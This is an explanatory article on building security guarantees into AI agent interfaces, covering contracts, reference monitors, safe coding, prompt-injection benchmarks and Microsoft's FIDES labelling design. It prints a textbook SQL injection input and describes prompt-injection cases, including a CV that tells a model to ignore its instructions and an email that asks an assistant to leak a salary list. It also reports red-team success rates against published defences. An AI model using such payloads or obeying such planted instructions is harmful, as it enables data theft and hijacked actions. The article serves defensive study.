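# Assurance by construction for AI systems: guarantees built into interfaces

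## What it means to build a guarantee into an interface

Assurance by construction means designing a system so that its structure guarantees a stated property, and engineers don't have to infer that property from tests of the system's behaviour. It is a general approach used in several fields, not a single method. "Assurance" here has its engineering sense of grounds for justified confidence in a claim about a system, a definition that *Modular Assurance of Complex Systems Using Contract-Based Design Principles* (McGeorge and Glomsrud, 2024) takes from an international standard. The usual alternative is post-hoc testing, in which engineers run the finished system on sample inputs, including attacks, and estimate how often it fails. The choice matters for AI because engineers can prove very little about what a large language model will output, but they fully control what the software around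 it accepts.

Suppose an email assistant uses a language model that can read a person's mail and files, including a salary list, and can send messages. A stranger emails the person and includes an instruction for the assistant to forward the list to an outside address.

The engineers can test for this leak by writing, say, a thousand malicious emails, feeding them to the assistant and counting how often the list gets out. If it never does, they can be 95 per cent confident that the leak rate is below about 0.3 per cent. That figure holds only for emails drawn in the same way as the thousand, and an attacker can write a different kind.

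Or they can change the send function. The owner marks certain files "private". The software around the model copies that mark onto anything the model writes after reading such a file, and the send function rejects every marked message to an outside address. The stranger's email may still cause the model to try, but the attempt fails however the email is worded. The rule also blocks legitimate messages. The assistant can no longer send the list to the owner's outside accountant, and once the model has read the list, even a reply about lunch carries the mark. Finer rules for combining marks exist. The guarantee covers only one kind of leak and doesn't ensure that the assistant summarises mail correctly or avoids deleting the wrong message.

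### Contracts between components

An interface contract states what a component may assume about its inputs and what it guarantees in return. *Contracts in System Development* (Hugues and Procter, 2023) gives the example of a routine that sets the seconds on a clock. The routine requires a number from 0 to 59 and guarantees that the clock will then show that number. If another program passes it 75, the contract guarantees nothing about the result.

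Incer, Badithela and colleagues (2023), in *Pacti*, a paper on a software tool for calculating with contracts, set out the standard general form. Start from the set of all behaviours, where a behaviour is one complete history of the system's variables. A component M is the set of behaviours it can show, and a property is the set of behaviours that meet some criterion, so M has a property P when M ⊆ P. Two components running together can show only the behaviours open to both, M ∩ M′. A contract is then a pair of properties (A, G), an assumption and a guarantee. M implements the contract if M ∩ E ⊆ G for every environment E that satisfies A. Since A is itself the largest such environment, this comes down to

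M ∩ A ⊆ G, or equivalently M ⊆ G ∪ ¬A,

where ¬A stands for all behaviours outside A. The second version makes plain that a behaviour can comply in either of two ways: the guarantee holds, or the assumption was false to begin with. *A Mechanically Verified Theory of Contracts* (2021) writes this directly into its definition of satisfaction.

The email assistant needs two contracts. The first belongs to the runtime, the software that fetches files for the model and carries out its requests:

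- A₁: the owner has marked every private file.
- G₁: every private file, and all text the model writes after reading one, carries the mark.

The second belongs to the send function:

- A₂: every message containing material from a private file carries the mark.
- G₂: no message containing material from a private file goes to an outside address.

An engineer composes the two contracts to find what the pair guarantees together. *Pacti* gives the combined guarantee as (G₁ ∪ ¬A₁) ∩ (G₂ ∪ ¬A₂) and the combined assumption as (A₁ ∩ A₂) ∪ (A₁ ∩ ¬G₁) ∪ (A₂ ∩ ¬G₂). Incer and colleagues call the last two pieces of the assumption "failure terms" because they describe a component that received what it needed but did not deliver what it guaranteed. If the model is the only thing that composes messages, A₁ and G₁ together imply A₂, which means the runtime supplies what the send function needs. A theorem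 in the same paper then allows the engineer to use the simpler, looser contract (A₁, G₂) instead. Under this contract, if the owner has marked every private file, no message containing material from one goes outside.

The language model has no contract in this derivation, so the result holds whatever the model does. A company could swap in a different model without redoing the derivation. It could also replace the send function, provided the new function's contract refines the old one. *Contract-Based Decomposition of Temporal Logic Specifications for Networked Systems under Arbitrary Partitions* (2026) states that the new contract must not assume more or guarantee less than the old one.

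If the owner forgets to mark the salary list, A₁ is false, so the runtime passes along unmarked text. A₂ is then false too, and the send function sends the message. The list leaks even though both components met their contracts, so testing either one against its contract would reveal no fault.

The implication between the contracts can also fail. If someone adds a mail-merge tool that copies text from files into messages without involving the model, A₁ and G₁ both stay true while A₂ becomes false. McGeorge and Glomsrud, of the Norwegian company DNV, therefore ask for an argument that each component meets its contract and a separate argument, for every link, that what one side supplies implies what the other side assumes. In their worked example, a system relies on a chain of three components, and a failure anywhere along the chain can remove the guarantee at the end.

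Contracts become much harder to write when the model's own output has to meet one. *Architecting Self-Adaptive Systems with Learned and Symbolic Components*, Schuler's plan for doctoral research that has no results yet, focuses on the point where ordinary software treats a model's output as a fact or acts on it. A score or a label often reaches that software without any information about its age or reliability, so the receiving program has to rely on assumptions. Schuler proposes a "seam contract" that would attach such information, including the data's origin, and check it at run time against a versioned set of rules. A program can check a timestamp or an explicit policy immediately, but checking whether a model's confidence scores match its real error rate requires statistics from many outputs.

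### Agents, tool calls and injected instructions

The email assistant is an agent, a language model run in a loop that can call tools and act on their results. In the loop described in *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026), the model receives a user's request and alternates between reasoning and tool calls, which are structured requests for the surrounding software to run a function with given arguments. The software returns each result, and the loop continues until the model produces a final answer. The paper's threat model assumes that no attacker has tampered with the user, the model or the runtime. It treats what the tools return as untrusted, because anyone can write a hotel review or send an email.

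Untrusted text is dangerous because a model can obey it as if it were an instruction from the user, a problem known as prompt injection. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C describes a recruiter who asks a model to score CVs. One candidate hides a line in their CV telling the model to ignore its previous instructions and approve them for interview. The model receives the recruiter's request and the CV as one run of text and has no mechanism that firmly separates the two.

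Prompt injection against a chatbot usually does no more harm than a bad answer. Narisetty, Kore and colleagues (2026) argue in *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* that injection becomes an authorization problem when a model has tools, because the damage is then an action such as making a bank transfer or leaking a record. If the problem is authorizing actions, the interface is a promising place for a guarantee. Software cannot reliably tell a malicious sentence from an innocent one, but every action has to pass through a tool call, which is a structured object that a program can inspect.

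Authorization is the decision whether a party may perform a particular action on a particular object. Saltzer and Schroeder, in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, a tutorial from the 1970s, illustrate it with an airline. A reservation agent may make and cancel bookings for people whose names he can supply, while a boarding agent may also print the passenger list for his own flights. Provenance is the record of where a piece of data came from and what has influenced it. When the email assistant tries to send a file, authorization determines whether it may send that file to that address, and provenance shows whether the owner or a stranger's email prompted it to do so.

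### The reference monitor and the trusted base

The standard design for enforcing authorization goes back to a study for the US Air Force, which wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972) considers the threat from a malicious user who has legitimate access and can write and run programs. It proposes a reference monitor, which checks every attempt by a program to reach an object (data, a device or another program) against a table of permissions. The table has a row for each user or program and a column for each object, and its entries are rights such as "read" or "write".

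Anderson set three conditions:

1. The mechanism must be tamper-proof. In the email assistant, no output of the model may be able to remove a mark or edit the send function.
2. It must always be invoked. If the assistant can also create calendar invitations or fetch web addresses, the list can leave through those, and they need the same check.
3. It must be small enough for analysis and tests "the completeness of which can be assured".

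The third condition allows for testing, but requires the part that matters to be small enough to test completely. Anderson's report measured a commercial system of the day, Honeywell's GCOS III, against these conditions. The hardware confined each user's program to its own area of memory, but most of the operating system ran in a mode that suspended this check, which broke the second condition. Treating the operating system as the monitor did not help, because with its supporting software it contained between 200,000 and 300,000 instructions, far too many to analyse. The report also points out that "tiger teams", experts hired to break into a system, reveal a flaw if they succeed, but if they fail, the system's security remains unknown. As of 1972, every known team had succeeded.

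A guarantee's trusted base is the set of parts that must work correctly for the guarantee to hold. For the email assistant, it consists of the runtime, the send function, the store that keeps the marks, the underlying operating system and hardware, and an owner who marks files correctly. It does not include the model. Anderson stated explicitly that the reference monitor depends on reliable identification of users, physical security, protected communication lines and working hardware. For agents, Narisetty and colleagues identify the weak point as how provenance is assigned, which they found under-specified in every defence they surveyed. Designers generally treat the user's input as trustworthy, so if a user pastes a stranger's text into a request, the record of its origin is wrong from the start.

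Two of Saltzer and Schroeder's design principles limit the harm when part of the base fails. Under least privilege, every program runs with only the rights its job requires, so an assistant asked only to summarise mail gets no send function. Under fail-safe defaults, access is denied unless explicitly permitted. They reason that a mistake in a list of permissions blocks something legitimate and somebody soon complains, whereas a mistake in a list of prohibitions lets something through and may go unnoticed. The forgotten salary list is a mistake of the second kind. If the runtime treated every file as private until the owner marked it public, forgetting to mark a file would block a message instead of causing a leak. They also warn that concentrating on mechanisms that are logically impossible to defeat can create false confidence in the whole system.

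### The confused deputy

A permission check can work as its designers intended and still allow harm. In *The Confused Deputy*, Hardy tells a nearly true story from Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Users could run a compiler and name a file to receive its debugging output. The compiler also kept usage statistics in a system directory, so the administrators had given it permission to write files there. The company's billing records were in the same directory. One user named the billing file as the destination for the debugging output. The operating system allowed the request because the compiler had permission to write in that directory, and the billing information was lost.

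The compiler was a confused deputy, a program tricked into misusing authority that it holds for someone else. It had one authority from the user and another from the administrators, and no way to indicate which it was using for a particular write. Hardy rejects having the compiler check file names because the list of sensitive files keeps changing and some users may have a legitimate reason to write in that directory. His remedy is a capability, an unforgeable value that both names a resource and grants the right to use it. The administrators give the compiler a capability for the statistics file. A user who wants debugging output gives it a capability for the output file, so a user without a capability for the billing file cannot direct the output there.

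An agent that reads a stranger's email while holding its owner's right to send files is in much the same position as the compiler. The send function receives a request from the assistant, which has permission. David C calls language models "inherently confusable" deputies, because nobody knows how to remove the confusion from inside the model, and recommends limiting the system's actions with ordinary deterministic software. The post also includes a rule from an exchange between Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista: when a model processes information from some party, the model's privileges drop to that party's level.

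The rule is sound, but it restricts a lot of useful work that requires acting on what strangers write. Narisetty and colleagues give the example of an assistant told to read an email and, if it is a meeting request, add the meeting to the calendar. There, the untrusted text has to determine what the assistant does. Current designs mostly ask the user to approve such steps, and people who see many approval requests stop reading them. Narisetty and colleagues regard this as the deepest open problem in the area, and it is a serious objection to any design that relies on keeping untrusted data away from consequential actions.

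### From correct programs to other properties

The term "by construction" comes from software engineering. In correctness by construction, developers start from a precise specification and refine it into code in small steps, using rules that preserve correctness at each step. *X-by-Construction Meets AI* (ter Beek, Cleophas and colleagues, 2025) explains that testing then serves to validate the process rather than to find bugs. From 2018, a series of research meetings extended the idea to "X-by-construction", where X can be security, reliability, energy use or some other property beyond functional correctness. Later meetings covered probabilistic systems and monitoring at run time, and the 2024 meeting focused on AI.

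The original method is hard to apply to AI because a model learned from data has no specification from which to refine it step by step. ter Beek and colleagues accept that AI components make it difficult, perhaps impossible, to ensure correctness at design time. One response is to leave the model unchanged and build the desired property into the system around it. Among the 2024 contributions, Wenzel and colleagues did this for accountability. Their "Decision Bill of Materials" is a cryptographically signed record of the data, programs and people behind an AI system's decision. A separate program can use it to verify whether the decision meets a certification standard, but the record does not show whether the decision was a good one.

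### AgentDojo, the common yardstick

Research on agent defences relies heavily on *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024), a benchmark that simulates an office suite, a Slack workspace, a travel agency and a bank, and gives the agent tools to work in them. It has 97 user tasks, such as paying a bill stored in a file, and 27 injection tasks, such as sending as much money as possible to the attacker. The benchmark pairs each user task with every injection task from the same environment, which gives 629 security cases. The injected text sits where a stranger could plausibly have put it, such as the body of an email. After each run, ordinary code checks the state of the simulated environment to see whether the bill was paid or money was sent to the attacker. *AgentDojo* does not use a language model as the judge because a successful injection might hijack the judge too.

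AgentDojo's two main measures are the share of user tasks the agent completes, with or without an attack, and the share of security cases in which the attacker succeeds. Neither measure means much alone, since an agent that does nothing resists every attack. In the original experiments, the 2024 models completed fewer than 66 per cent of tasks when there was no attack. Attacks succeeded against the best-performing agents in fewer than 25 per cent of cases, and in 8 per cent when a separate detector screened for injections.

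Comparisons between papers need care. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) counts over 900 combinations of tasks and attacks, so not every published score is based on the original 629. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) found that the injected text sometimes overwrites information the user's task requires, such as the contents of the bill, so even an agent that ignores the attack cannot finish the task.

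AgentDojo's larger limitation is that its supplied attacks are fixed in advance. Debenedetti and colleagues meant other researchers to add attacks adapted to each new defence, but most evaluations use the supplied ones, and Ma and colleagues found that the resulting scores often overstate how well a defence works. For a defence that rests on a contract, a low attack score is weaker evidence than the argument behind the contract. A successful attack is more informative because it means that an assumption was false, the implementation has a bug, or the attacker's goal lay outside the guarantee. The share of tasks completed measures how much useful work the restrictions prevent, which the contract does not describe.

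## How databases stopped injected commands, and what happened to filters for AI agents

Database programmers faced a version of prompt injection long before language models existed, and they largely solved it by changing an interface. Websites keep records in databases and retrieve them with commands in a language called SQL. These commands often have to include something a visitor typed, such as a name, and the visitor may be hostile.

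### SQL injection and the parameterized query

Suppose a shop's website looks up a customer's orders with this line:

```
query = "SELECT total FROM orders WHERE customer = '" + name + "'"
```

If the visitor types `Ada`, the database receives a command ending in `customer = 'Ada'` and returns Ada's orders. If the visitor types `x' OR '1'='1`, the database receives this:

```
SELECT total FROM orders WHERE customer = 'x' OR '1'='1'
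```

In this attack, called SQL injection, the quotation mark after the x closes the name early, so the database reads the rest of the visitor's text as part of the command. Since '1' always equals '1', the condition holds for every row, and the visitor gets everybody's orders.

In a parameterized query, the program sends the command and the visitor's text separately:

```
query = "SELECT total FROM orders WHERE customer = ?"
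run(query, name)
```

The database first parses the command, which fixes it as a comparison between one column and one value. It binds the visitor's text to the question mark only after that. It therefore treats the hostile string as a customer's name, finds no match, and returns nothing. According to David C, the database engine can never interpret a bound value as an instruction. This protection doesn't depend on anyone recognising an attack. A filter that rejected quotation marks would turn away a customer called O'Brien, but the parameterized query finds her orders.

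A parameterized query guarantees only the structure of the command. If the website lets any visitor look up any name, a stranger can type `Ada` and read her orders. That is an authorization failure, which parameterized queries do not address.

According to David C, SQL injection attacks peaked around 2010, and better defaults came only after a decade of breaches. The flaw is now rare in websites but still occurs in software generally. In *An Overview of Google's Commitment to Secure by Design* (2024), Google cites a list of persistent software weaknesses that ranks SQL injection third.

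### Google's safe coding

Parameterized queries protect a program only where programmers remember to use them. The usual database function accepts any string, so a programmer who builds a query by joining strings gets no warning. *Safe Coding* (Kern, 2025) gives the example of a function called `getWidgetsBy`, which takes a search condition and pastes it into a query. All code that calls this function must keep visitors' text out of the condition, and in a large program no developer can check every call. The database function cannot check either, because a query's safety depends on where its text came from, and an ordinary string does not record that.

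Google put that record into the type. A type is the category a programming language gives to a value, such as "whole number" or "text". The compiler, which translates source code into a form the machine can run, rejects code that passes a value of the wrong type. Google's database functions now accept only a `TrustedSqlString` instead of plain text. Only a few builder functions can create one, and they take only text that a developer wrote into the source code. A visitor's input does not exist yet when the compiler runs, so the developer has no ordinary way to put it in the query. Code that tries to do so fails to compile, and the developer must send the input as a bound value instead.

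The type is an interface contract, as defined in the previous section. The database function assumes that developers wrote every part of the query, and the compiler checks that assumption at every call. Google's build system blocks the old functions by default, but some code still needs them, so security experts review each request for an exception. The trusted base consists of the builders, the reviewed exceptions and the compiler. Experts usually reason about the builders by hand instead of formally proving them correct, but the builders are a small and stable part of the code.

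Google applied the same method to cross-site scripting (XSS), in which an attacker's text ends up in a web page and runs as a program in another visitor's browser. In *If It's Not Secure, It Should Not Compile*, Wang, Bangert and Kern describe how they listed the browser functions that can run text as code, made the compiler reject code that uses them, and supplied safe replacements.

Google has published results for both kinds of bug:

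- It began the SQL work in 2013 and, by 2024, had seen no SQL injection vulnerability in a decade across hundreds of applications built on the new functions.
- Hundreds of complex web applications built on the hardened frameworks averaged less than one XSS report a year in total over three years.
- In its core products, which include older code that engineers had to convert, XSS vulnerabilities fell by 90 per cent over a decade.

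Wang and colleagues also followed one product with a few tens of engineers working on its web pages. It had ten XSS bugs of the relevant type in the year before it adopted the method, two in the year it made the change and one in the year after.

None of this comes from a controlled experiment, and Google introduced other protections over the same period. The most persuasive evidence that the new functions helped is where the remaining bugs were. Across the company, XSS made up a shrinking share of serious reports from outsiders, while a growing share of the XSS bugs came from old code that did not use the new functions, even though the amount of old code was falling. A general improvement in security would presumably have helped old and new code alike.

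The work involved was modest for a company of Google's size. The single product took about a year to convert. Across the company, experts received fewer than eight requests for exceptions a week in the early months, and by the end of 2020 fewer than 1 per cent of over a million JavaScript files had an exemption. The method would take more work at a smaller organisation without a shared code repository and compulsory code review.

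Safe coding also assumes that developers mean well. Kern points out that a determined programmer could build a `TrustedSqlString` that the compiler accepts by copying a visitor's text character by character from a table containing every letter of the alphabet. He reports that this is not a significant problem at Google, because trusted developers are very unlikely to write something so obviously wrong. The same reasoning doesn't apply to an agent that writes its own code, because a stranger's email may have influenced what it writes.

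### Filters and trained refusals

When prompt injection appeared, most defences relied on the model, or a separate program, to recognise hostile text. Some developers put a filter in front of the model to detect injections. Others trained the model on examples of attacks so that it would ignore them. Others changed the prompt. Spotlighting, for example, uses special markers to separate trusted from untrusted text, and Prompt Sandwiching repeats the user's request after the untrusted text so that the model still follows it.

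Filters can make attacks harder, because an attacker has to deceive both the filter and the main model (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025, *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*). But many filters are language models, and Narisetty and colleagues note that an attacker can inject instructions into those too. A list of forbidden phrases works even less well, because an attacker can reword a request in endless ways. David C advises buyers to be wary of any product whose maker claims it stops prompt injection altogether.

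Developers mostly judged these defences by running a collection of known attacks and counting the successes. The scores were often close to zero.

### What a clean test can prove

Suppose a defence fails on any given attack with probability p, and that the attacks are independent of one another. The chance that it survives n attacks in a row is (1 − p)ⁿ. To find the highest failure rate that is still reasonably compatible with a clean record, set this chance to 5 per cent and solve for p:

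(1 − p)ⁿ = 0.05, so p = 1 − 0.05^(1/n) ≈ −ln(0.05)/n ≈ 3/n.

If the true rate were above about 3/n, a clean record over n tests would occur less than one time in twenty, so statisticians say with 95 per cent confidence that the rate is below 3/n. For the thousand emails in the previous section, the bound is 0.3 per cent. Showing that a rate is below one in a million would take about three million clean tests.

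Willison (2026), who named prompt injection in a 2022 blog post, describes a case where 6,000 injection attempts failed. The rule of three gives an upper bound of 0.05 per cent on the success rate per attempt. At that rate, an attacker who made a thousand further attempts would have about a 39 per cent chance of succeeding at least once.

This bound, too, holds only for attacks like the tested ones. Attackers look for whatever a researcher's collection lacks, and once they find an attack that works, they can use it every time. Willison likewise concludes that the 6,000 failed attempts give no assurance against somebody with a more sophisticated approach. He accepts that training models to resist injection appears to make attacks much harder, but advises against any system in which an injection could cause irreversible damage.

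### Twelve defences against attackers who adapt

In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025), a team that included researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, measured how much the choice of attacks matters. They attacked twelve published defences, using knowledge of how each one worked and plenty of computing power. Attack success had been near zero in the original tests of most of these defences, but the new attacks succeeded more than 90 per cent of the time against most of the twelve.

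The gap was especially wide for defences that change the prompt. AgentDojo's fixed attacks succeeded as little as 1 per cent of the time against Spotlighting and Prompt Sandwiching, while adapted attacks succeeded more than 95 per cent of the time against both. For adapted attacks, Narisetty and colleagues also list success rates of 96 per cent against MetaSecAlign, which trains the model on attacks, and above 90 per cent against the filters PromptGuard and Model Armor.

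The researchers also ran an online competition with more than 500 participants. Participants succeeded in every scenario, including those where the fixed attacks had failed. They produced 265 successful attacks against Spotlighting and 178 against Prompt Sandwiching.

These percentages do not rank the twelve defences, because the team tested each one on benchmarks suited to it. Some were meant to stop jailbreaks, in which the user tries to get forbidden output from the model, rather than injections by a third party. The team also did not try to measure how much effort a break requires, so a defence that failed might still deter a casual attacker. The study does establish that a near-zero score on fixed attacks is very weak evidence that a defence will stop a determined attacker. Rules that software enforces outside the model have had far fewer tests of this kind. In a small test of the permission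 system Progent, Narisetty and colleagues found that an adapted attack did no better than the standard ones.

### Repeated attempts

Attackers can usually try more than once, so laboratories have begun to publish the chance that at least one of several attempts succeeds. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* gives results for that model, which Anthropic has since replaced. Strong attacks succeeded 4.7 per cent of the time with one attempt, 33.6 per cent with ten and 63.0 per cent with a hundred. Some rival models had rates as high as 92 per cent.

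If every attempt had the same independent 4.7 per cent chance of success, at least one of ten attempts would succeed about 38 per cent of the time, and at least one of a hundred more than 99 per cent of the time. The measured rates rose more slowly, so engineers cannot calculate the risk from a hundred attempts using only the measured risk from one. A likely explanation is that some scenarios were easy to break and others very hard, so attackers broke the easy ones early and made little progress on the rest.

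The setting matters as much as the number of attempts. VentureBeat reported that Claude Opus 4.6, released in February 2026, resisted all 200 injection attempts in a restricted coding environment. When the same model controlled a computer through its graphical interface, a single attempt succeeded 17.8 per cent of the time. By the 200th attempt, the success rate was 78.6 per cent, or 57.1 per cent with added safeguards.

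Newer models resist prompt injection much better. *Anthropic's Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection* (Schneier, 2026) quotes results that Anthropic published in July 2026 for a benchmark by the security firm Gray Swan. Against Claude Opus 5, one attempt succeeded 0.2 per cent of the time, and 15 attempts succeeded 2.0 per cent of the time. The table also includes a figure for Claude Fable 5 from The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser based prompt injection*.

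| Model | Attack success within 15 attempts |
|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | 2.0% |
| Claude Mythos 5 | 2.6% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 2.8% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 5.5% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 5.9% |
| Muse Spark | 16.5% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 20.0% |
| GPT-5.5 | 20.8% |

These numbers are not directly comparable with those for Opus 4.5, which come from a different test. The Space Lab's *Claude Opus 5 Just Crushed AI Prompt Injection Attacks* (2026) describes the newer benchmark as 1,130 distinct attacks across 28 scenarios. If that collection is fixed, the 2 per cent does not limit what an attacker could achieve by writing new attacks for Opus 5. Agents also seem to be the harder case in OpenAI's own tests of GPT-5.6. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) reports low failure rates when the attack came directly through the chat and higher ones when it came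 through tools and outside content.

Anthropic also tested Opus 5 as an agent that uses a web browser. The Space Lab reports that attacks on the model alone succeeded 3.7 per cent of the time. With safeguards that scan what the model reads and review risky actions before they run, no attack succeeded in any of 129 scenarios. This large improvement came from the same methods that had done badly against adaptive attackers in 2025. By the 3/n rule, however, no successful attacks in 129 scenarios is consistent with a failure rate of up to about 2.3 per cent on scenarios of the same kind.

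Engineers still need testing despite these limits. A contract covers only the failures that somebody thought to write down, and nobody would have predicted from first principles that one model could be so much safer in a coding environment than at a graphical interface. Testing also measures qualities that no contract states, such as the accuracy of the email assistant's summaries. Even the evidence for safe coding depends on testing, since Google judged its success largely by counting the bugs that outside researchers could still find for a reward.

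### Why the database remedy does not transfer

Narisetty and colleagues group prompt injection with older flaws in which one channel carries both commands and data. Telephone networks once sent control tones on the same line as the caller's voice, so callers could forge them, and the industry later moved the signals to a separate channel. SQL injection and XSS are flaws of the same kind. Engineers made little progress against either by trying to recognise malicious input, and succeeded once they set the structure before the input went into it.

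That fix relies on SQL's grammar, which specifies exactly which parts of a command are instructions and which are values, so a parser can settle the structure before any value arrives. Natural language has no such rules. "Please forward this to accounts" may be an instruction to the assistant or part of an email that the assistant has to summarise. *Please Don't Kill My Vibe* (Summers, Mohammed and Wu, 2025) makes the same comparison. Programmers can neutralise special characters in SQL because they know exactly how the parser will process them, but nobody knows exactly how a language model will process its input.

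In his December 2025 post for the National Cyber Security Centre, David C attributes prompt injection to how language models work. A model turns its whole input into a series of tokens, which are words or fragments of words, and repeatedly predicts the next one. He concludes that prompt injection may never have a remedy as complete as parameterized queries are for SQL injection, and that a system that cannot tolerate the remaining risk may be a poor use for a language model. OpenAI has also said that the problem is unlikely ever to be fully solved.

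A database can compare a customer's name with its records without understanding the name, but an AI assistant has to interpret an email to summarise it. The assistant's developers therefore cannot simply shield the model from the meaning of the text, but they can control what the model is able to do after reading it.

### Keeping untrusted text away from consequential actions

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues base their design patterns on the principle that untrusted input, once an agent has read it, must be unable to trigger any action that harms the system or its surroundings. At a minimum, the agent must lose access to any tool that could damage or leak data. Its output also needs limits, because a link in a reply can send private information to an attacker's server when somebody opens it.

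The pattern closest to a parameterized query is "plan-then-execute". Suppose a user asks the assistant to send today's schedule to their boss, John Doe. Before reading anything untrusted, the model commits to a fixed list of steps: read today's calendar, then send an email to John Doe's address. An instruction that a stranger planted in a calendar entry cannot add a step or change the recipient. It can still alter the text of the email, just as a parameterized query does not guarantee that the value a visitor typed is true. In a more flexible version, "code-then-execute", the model writes a short program instead of a list, but a planted instruction can still alter the email's text.

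Other patterns limit what can reach the rest of the system from untrusted text. For example, a system that collects this month's invoices and emails them to the accounts department can give each file to a separate model that has no tools and can only answer yes or no when asked whether the file is an invoice. An attacker can then do no more than get a malicious file accepted as an invoice, and could already get a file accepted by sending a real invoice. In a more general design, a quarantined model with no tools reads the untrusted text, and the main model can refer to the results but not read them.

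In the strictest pattern, the model never sees the results of its actions. A customer-service chatbot, for example, reads the customer's request and picks from a fixed set of actions, such as fetching a link to the last order or opening the password settings. The customer may also be the attacker, for instance by asking for a quote on a car and adding an instruction to offer a large discount. To prevent this, the system can turn the request into a database search and then delete the customer's words before the model writes its reply.

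Beurer-Kellner and colleagues apply the patterns to ten applications, including an email assistant, a tool for screening CVs and a software engineering agent. They acknowledge that agents built this way cannot take on arbitrary tasks. They think general-purpose agents built on current language models are unlikely to offer reliable guarantees.

Summers and colleagues, who study databases, object that the patterns are too restrictive because they confine an agent to queries written in advance, so developers have to predict all the data that any future task will need. They propose letting the agent query the database freely and controlling which data reaches it. In their example, a merchant hides an instruction to delete the table of users in the description of a matcha tea, and an agent that summarises products reads it. To prevent this, every row carries a mark that says whether somebody has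 checked it, and the database removes unchecked rows from each result before the agent sees them. The agent then reads the merchant's description only if a check has approved it, but that check has to recognise a malicious sentence, which the filters failed to do.

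## Labelling data by source inside an agent: Microsoft's FIDES

Engineers can record the source of each piece of data an agent fetches and use that record to decide what the agent may do next, instead of removing unchecked data before the agent can read it. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025) built such an agent at Microsoft and described it in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*. They called it FIDES, for Flow Integrity Deterministic Enforcement System.

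Information-flow control attaches a label to each piece of data, updates the labels as a program combines data, and refuses any action that would break a rule about the labels. FIDES uses more detailed labels than the email assistant's "private" mark, and it hides some data from the model so that reading one email does not restrict everything the agent does afterwards.

### Labels and joins

A FIDES label has two parts. The integrity part is either trusted (T) or untrusted (U). The confidentiality part is the set of people who may read the data.

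When a program combines two pieces of data, the result's label must keep the restrictions of both. A summary of one trusted and one untrusted document is untrusted, because the untrusted one may have influenced the summary. If A, B and C may read one document, and B, C and D may read another, only B and C may read a summary of both.

Labels that combine like this form a lattice. Write x ⊑ y if label y is at least as restrictive as label x, so that data labelled x may flow to a place labelled y. Then T ⊑ U, and {A,B,C} ⊑ {B,C}, since a smaller set of readers is more restrictive. The join of two labels, x ⊔ y, is the least restrictive label that is at least as restrictive as both:

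- T ⊔ U = U
- {A,B,C} ⊔ {B,C,D} = {A,B,C} ∩ {B,C,D} = {B,C}
- (T, {A,B,C}) ⊔ (U, {B,C,D}) = (U, {B,C})

Costa and colleagues also describe a finer integrity label, which lists everyone who could have written the data. The join of two such labels is their union, because anyone who could have written either document could have influenced the summary.

A join can never make a label less restrictive. This makes the method safe, but it also means an agent that keeps reading will lose permissions and never regain them.

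### The labelled planning loop

Costa and colleagues divide an agent into a planner, which chooses the next step, and a loop, which carries it out. The planner can ask the loop to query the model, call a tool or finish with an answer. With labels added, a simple agent works like this:

1. The software around each tool labels the data that the tool returns. The user's request normally starts out trusted and public.
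2. The planner adds the new data to the conversation. The conversation's label becomes the join of its old label and the label on the new data.
3. The loop sends the conversation to the model and gives the model's response the conversation's label. Nobody can say reliably which parts of the input shaped the response, so the loop assumes that all of them did.
4. If the response is a tool call, the loop compares the labels on the call and its arguments with the policy for that tool.
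5. If the call breaks the policy, the loop stops it. Otherwise the loop runs the tool and returns to step 2 with the result. The result's label is the join of the labels on the call, its arguments and any stored data that the tool may read.

Anything the tool writes to storage gets the same label as the result. If the agent reads a stranger's email and then saves a note, the note is still untrusted when the agent opens it a week later.

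In the formal version of the loop, a forbidden call ends the run. In the experiments, the planner instead received a message that the policy had blocked the call and could try another way to finish the task.

### Two policies

The trusted-action policy covers consequential calls, such as bank transfers. It permits a call only if the join of the labels on the call and all its arguments is trusted. The permitted-flow policy covers calls that send data. It permits a call only if every recipient is permitted to read the data.

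Permitted flow alone does not stop prompt injection. A stranger's email could still make the agent send a message, but only to people already allowed to read what it says. Trusted action alone lets the owner share a secret on purpose. The email assistant could send the salary list to the owner's outside accountant if the owner asked for this and nothing untrusted had entered the conversation. Computer scientists call this robust declassification, which means that only a trusted party can decide to release a secret.

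For the experiments, Costa and colleagues assigned a policy to each tool. Sending an email had to satisfy either trusted action or permitted flow, transferring money had to satisfy trusted action, and adding guests to a calendar event had to satisfy both. They also loosened trusted action to check only the label on the call, not the labels on its arguments, and tightened permitted flow to block messages containing untrusted links.

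Neither policy protects the owner from the model's own mistakes. If the model misreads a trusted request and issues a call to pay the wrong person, the call carries a trusted label and the loop runs it. FIDES relies on the model to behave sensibly when it has seen only trusted text, though not to recognise an injection.

### Summarising three emails

One of the tasks that Costa and colleagues analyse is to summarise the top three emails in a mailbox and send the summary to somebody on Slack. Suppose that the recipient is a colleague of the user. An agent with a basic planner makes two calls:

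```
read_emails(number=3)
send_message(to=colleague, message="The three emails say ...")
```

The loop runs the first call, which came from the user's trusted request. The emails are untrusted and go straight into the conversation, so the conversation and the model's next response become untrusted too. That response is the request to send the message, and the loop refuses it under the trusted-action policy. It would refuse even if all three emails were harmless, because it checks only the label.

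FIDES avoids this by adapting a design that Willison (2023) proposed two years earlier in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*. The model Willison calls privileged has tools but never receives untrusted text. A second, quarantined model without tools reads that text. Ordinary software passes data between them, storing the untrusted text in variables and giving the privileged model only the variables' names.

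In FIDES, the planner's model plays the privileged role, and it makes three calls:

```
read_emails(number=3)                                 result: #emails
query_llm("Summarise these emails", input=#emails)    result: #summary
send_message(to=colleague, message=#summary)
```

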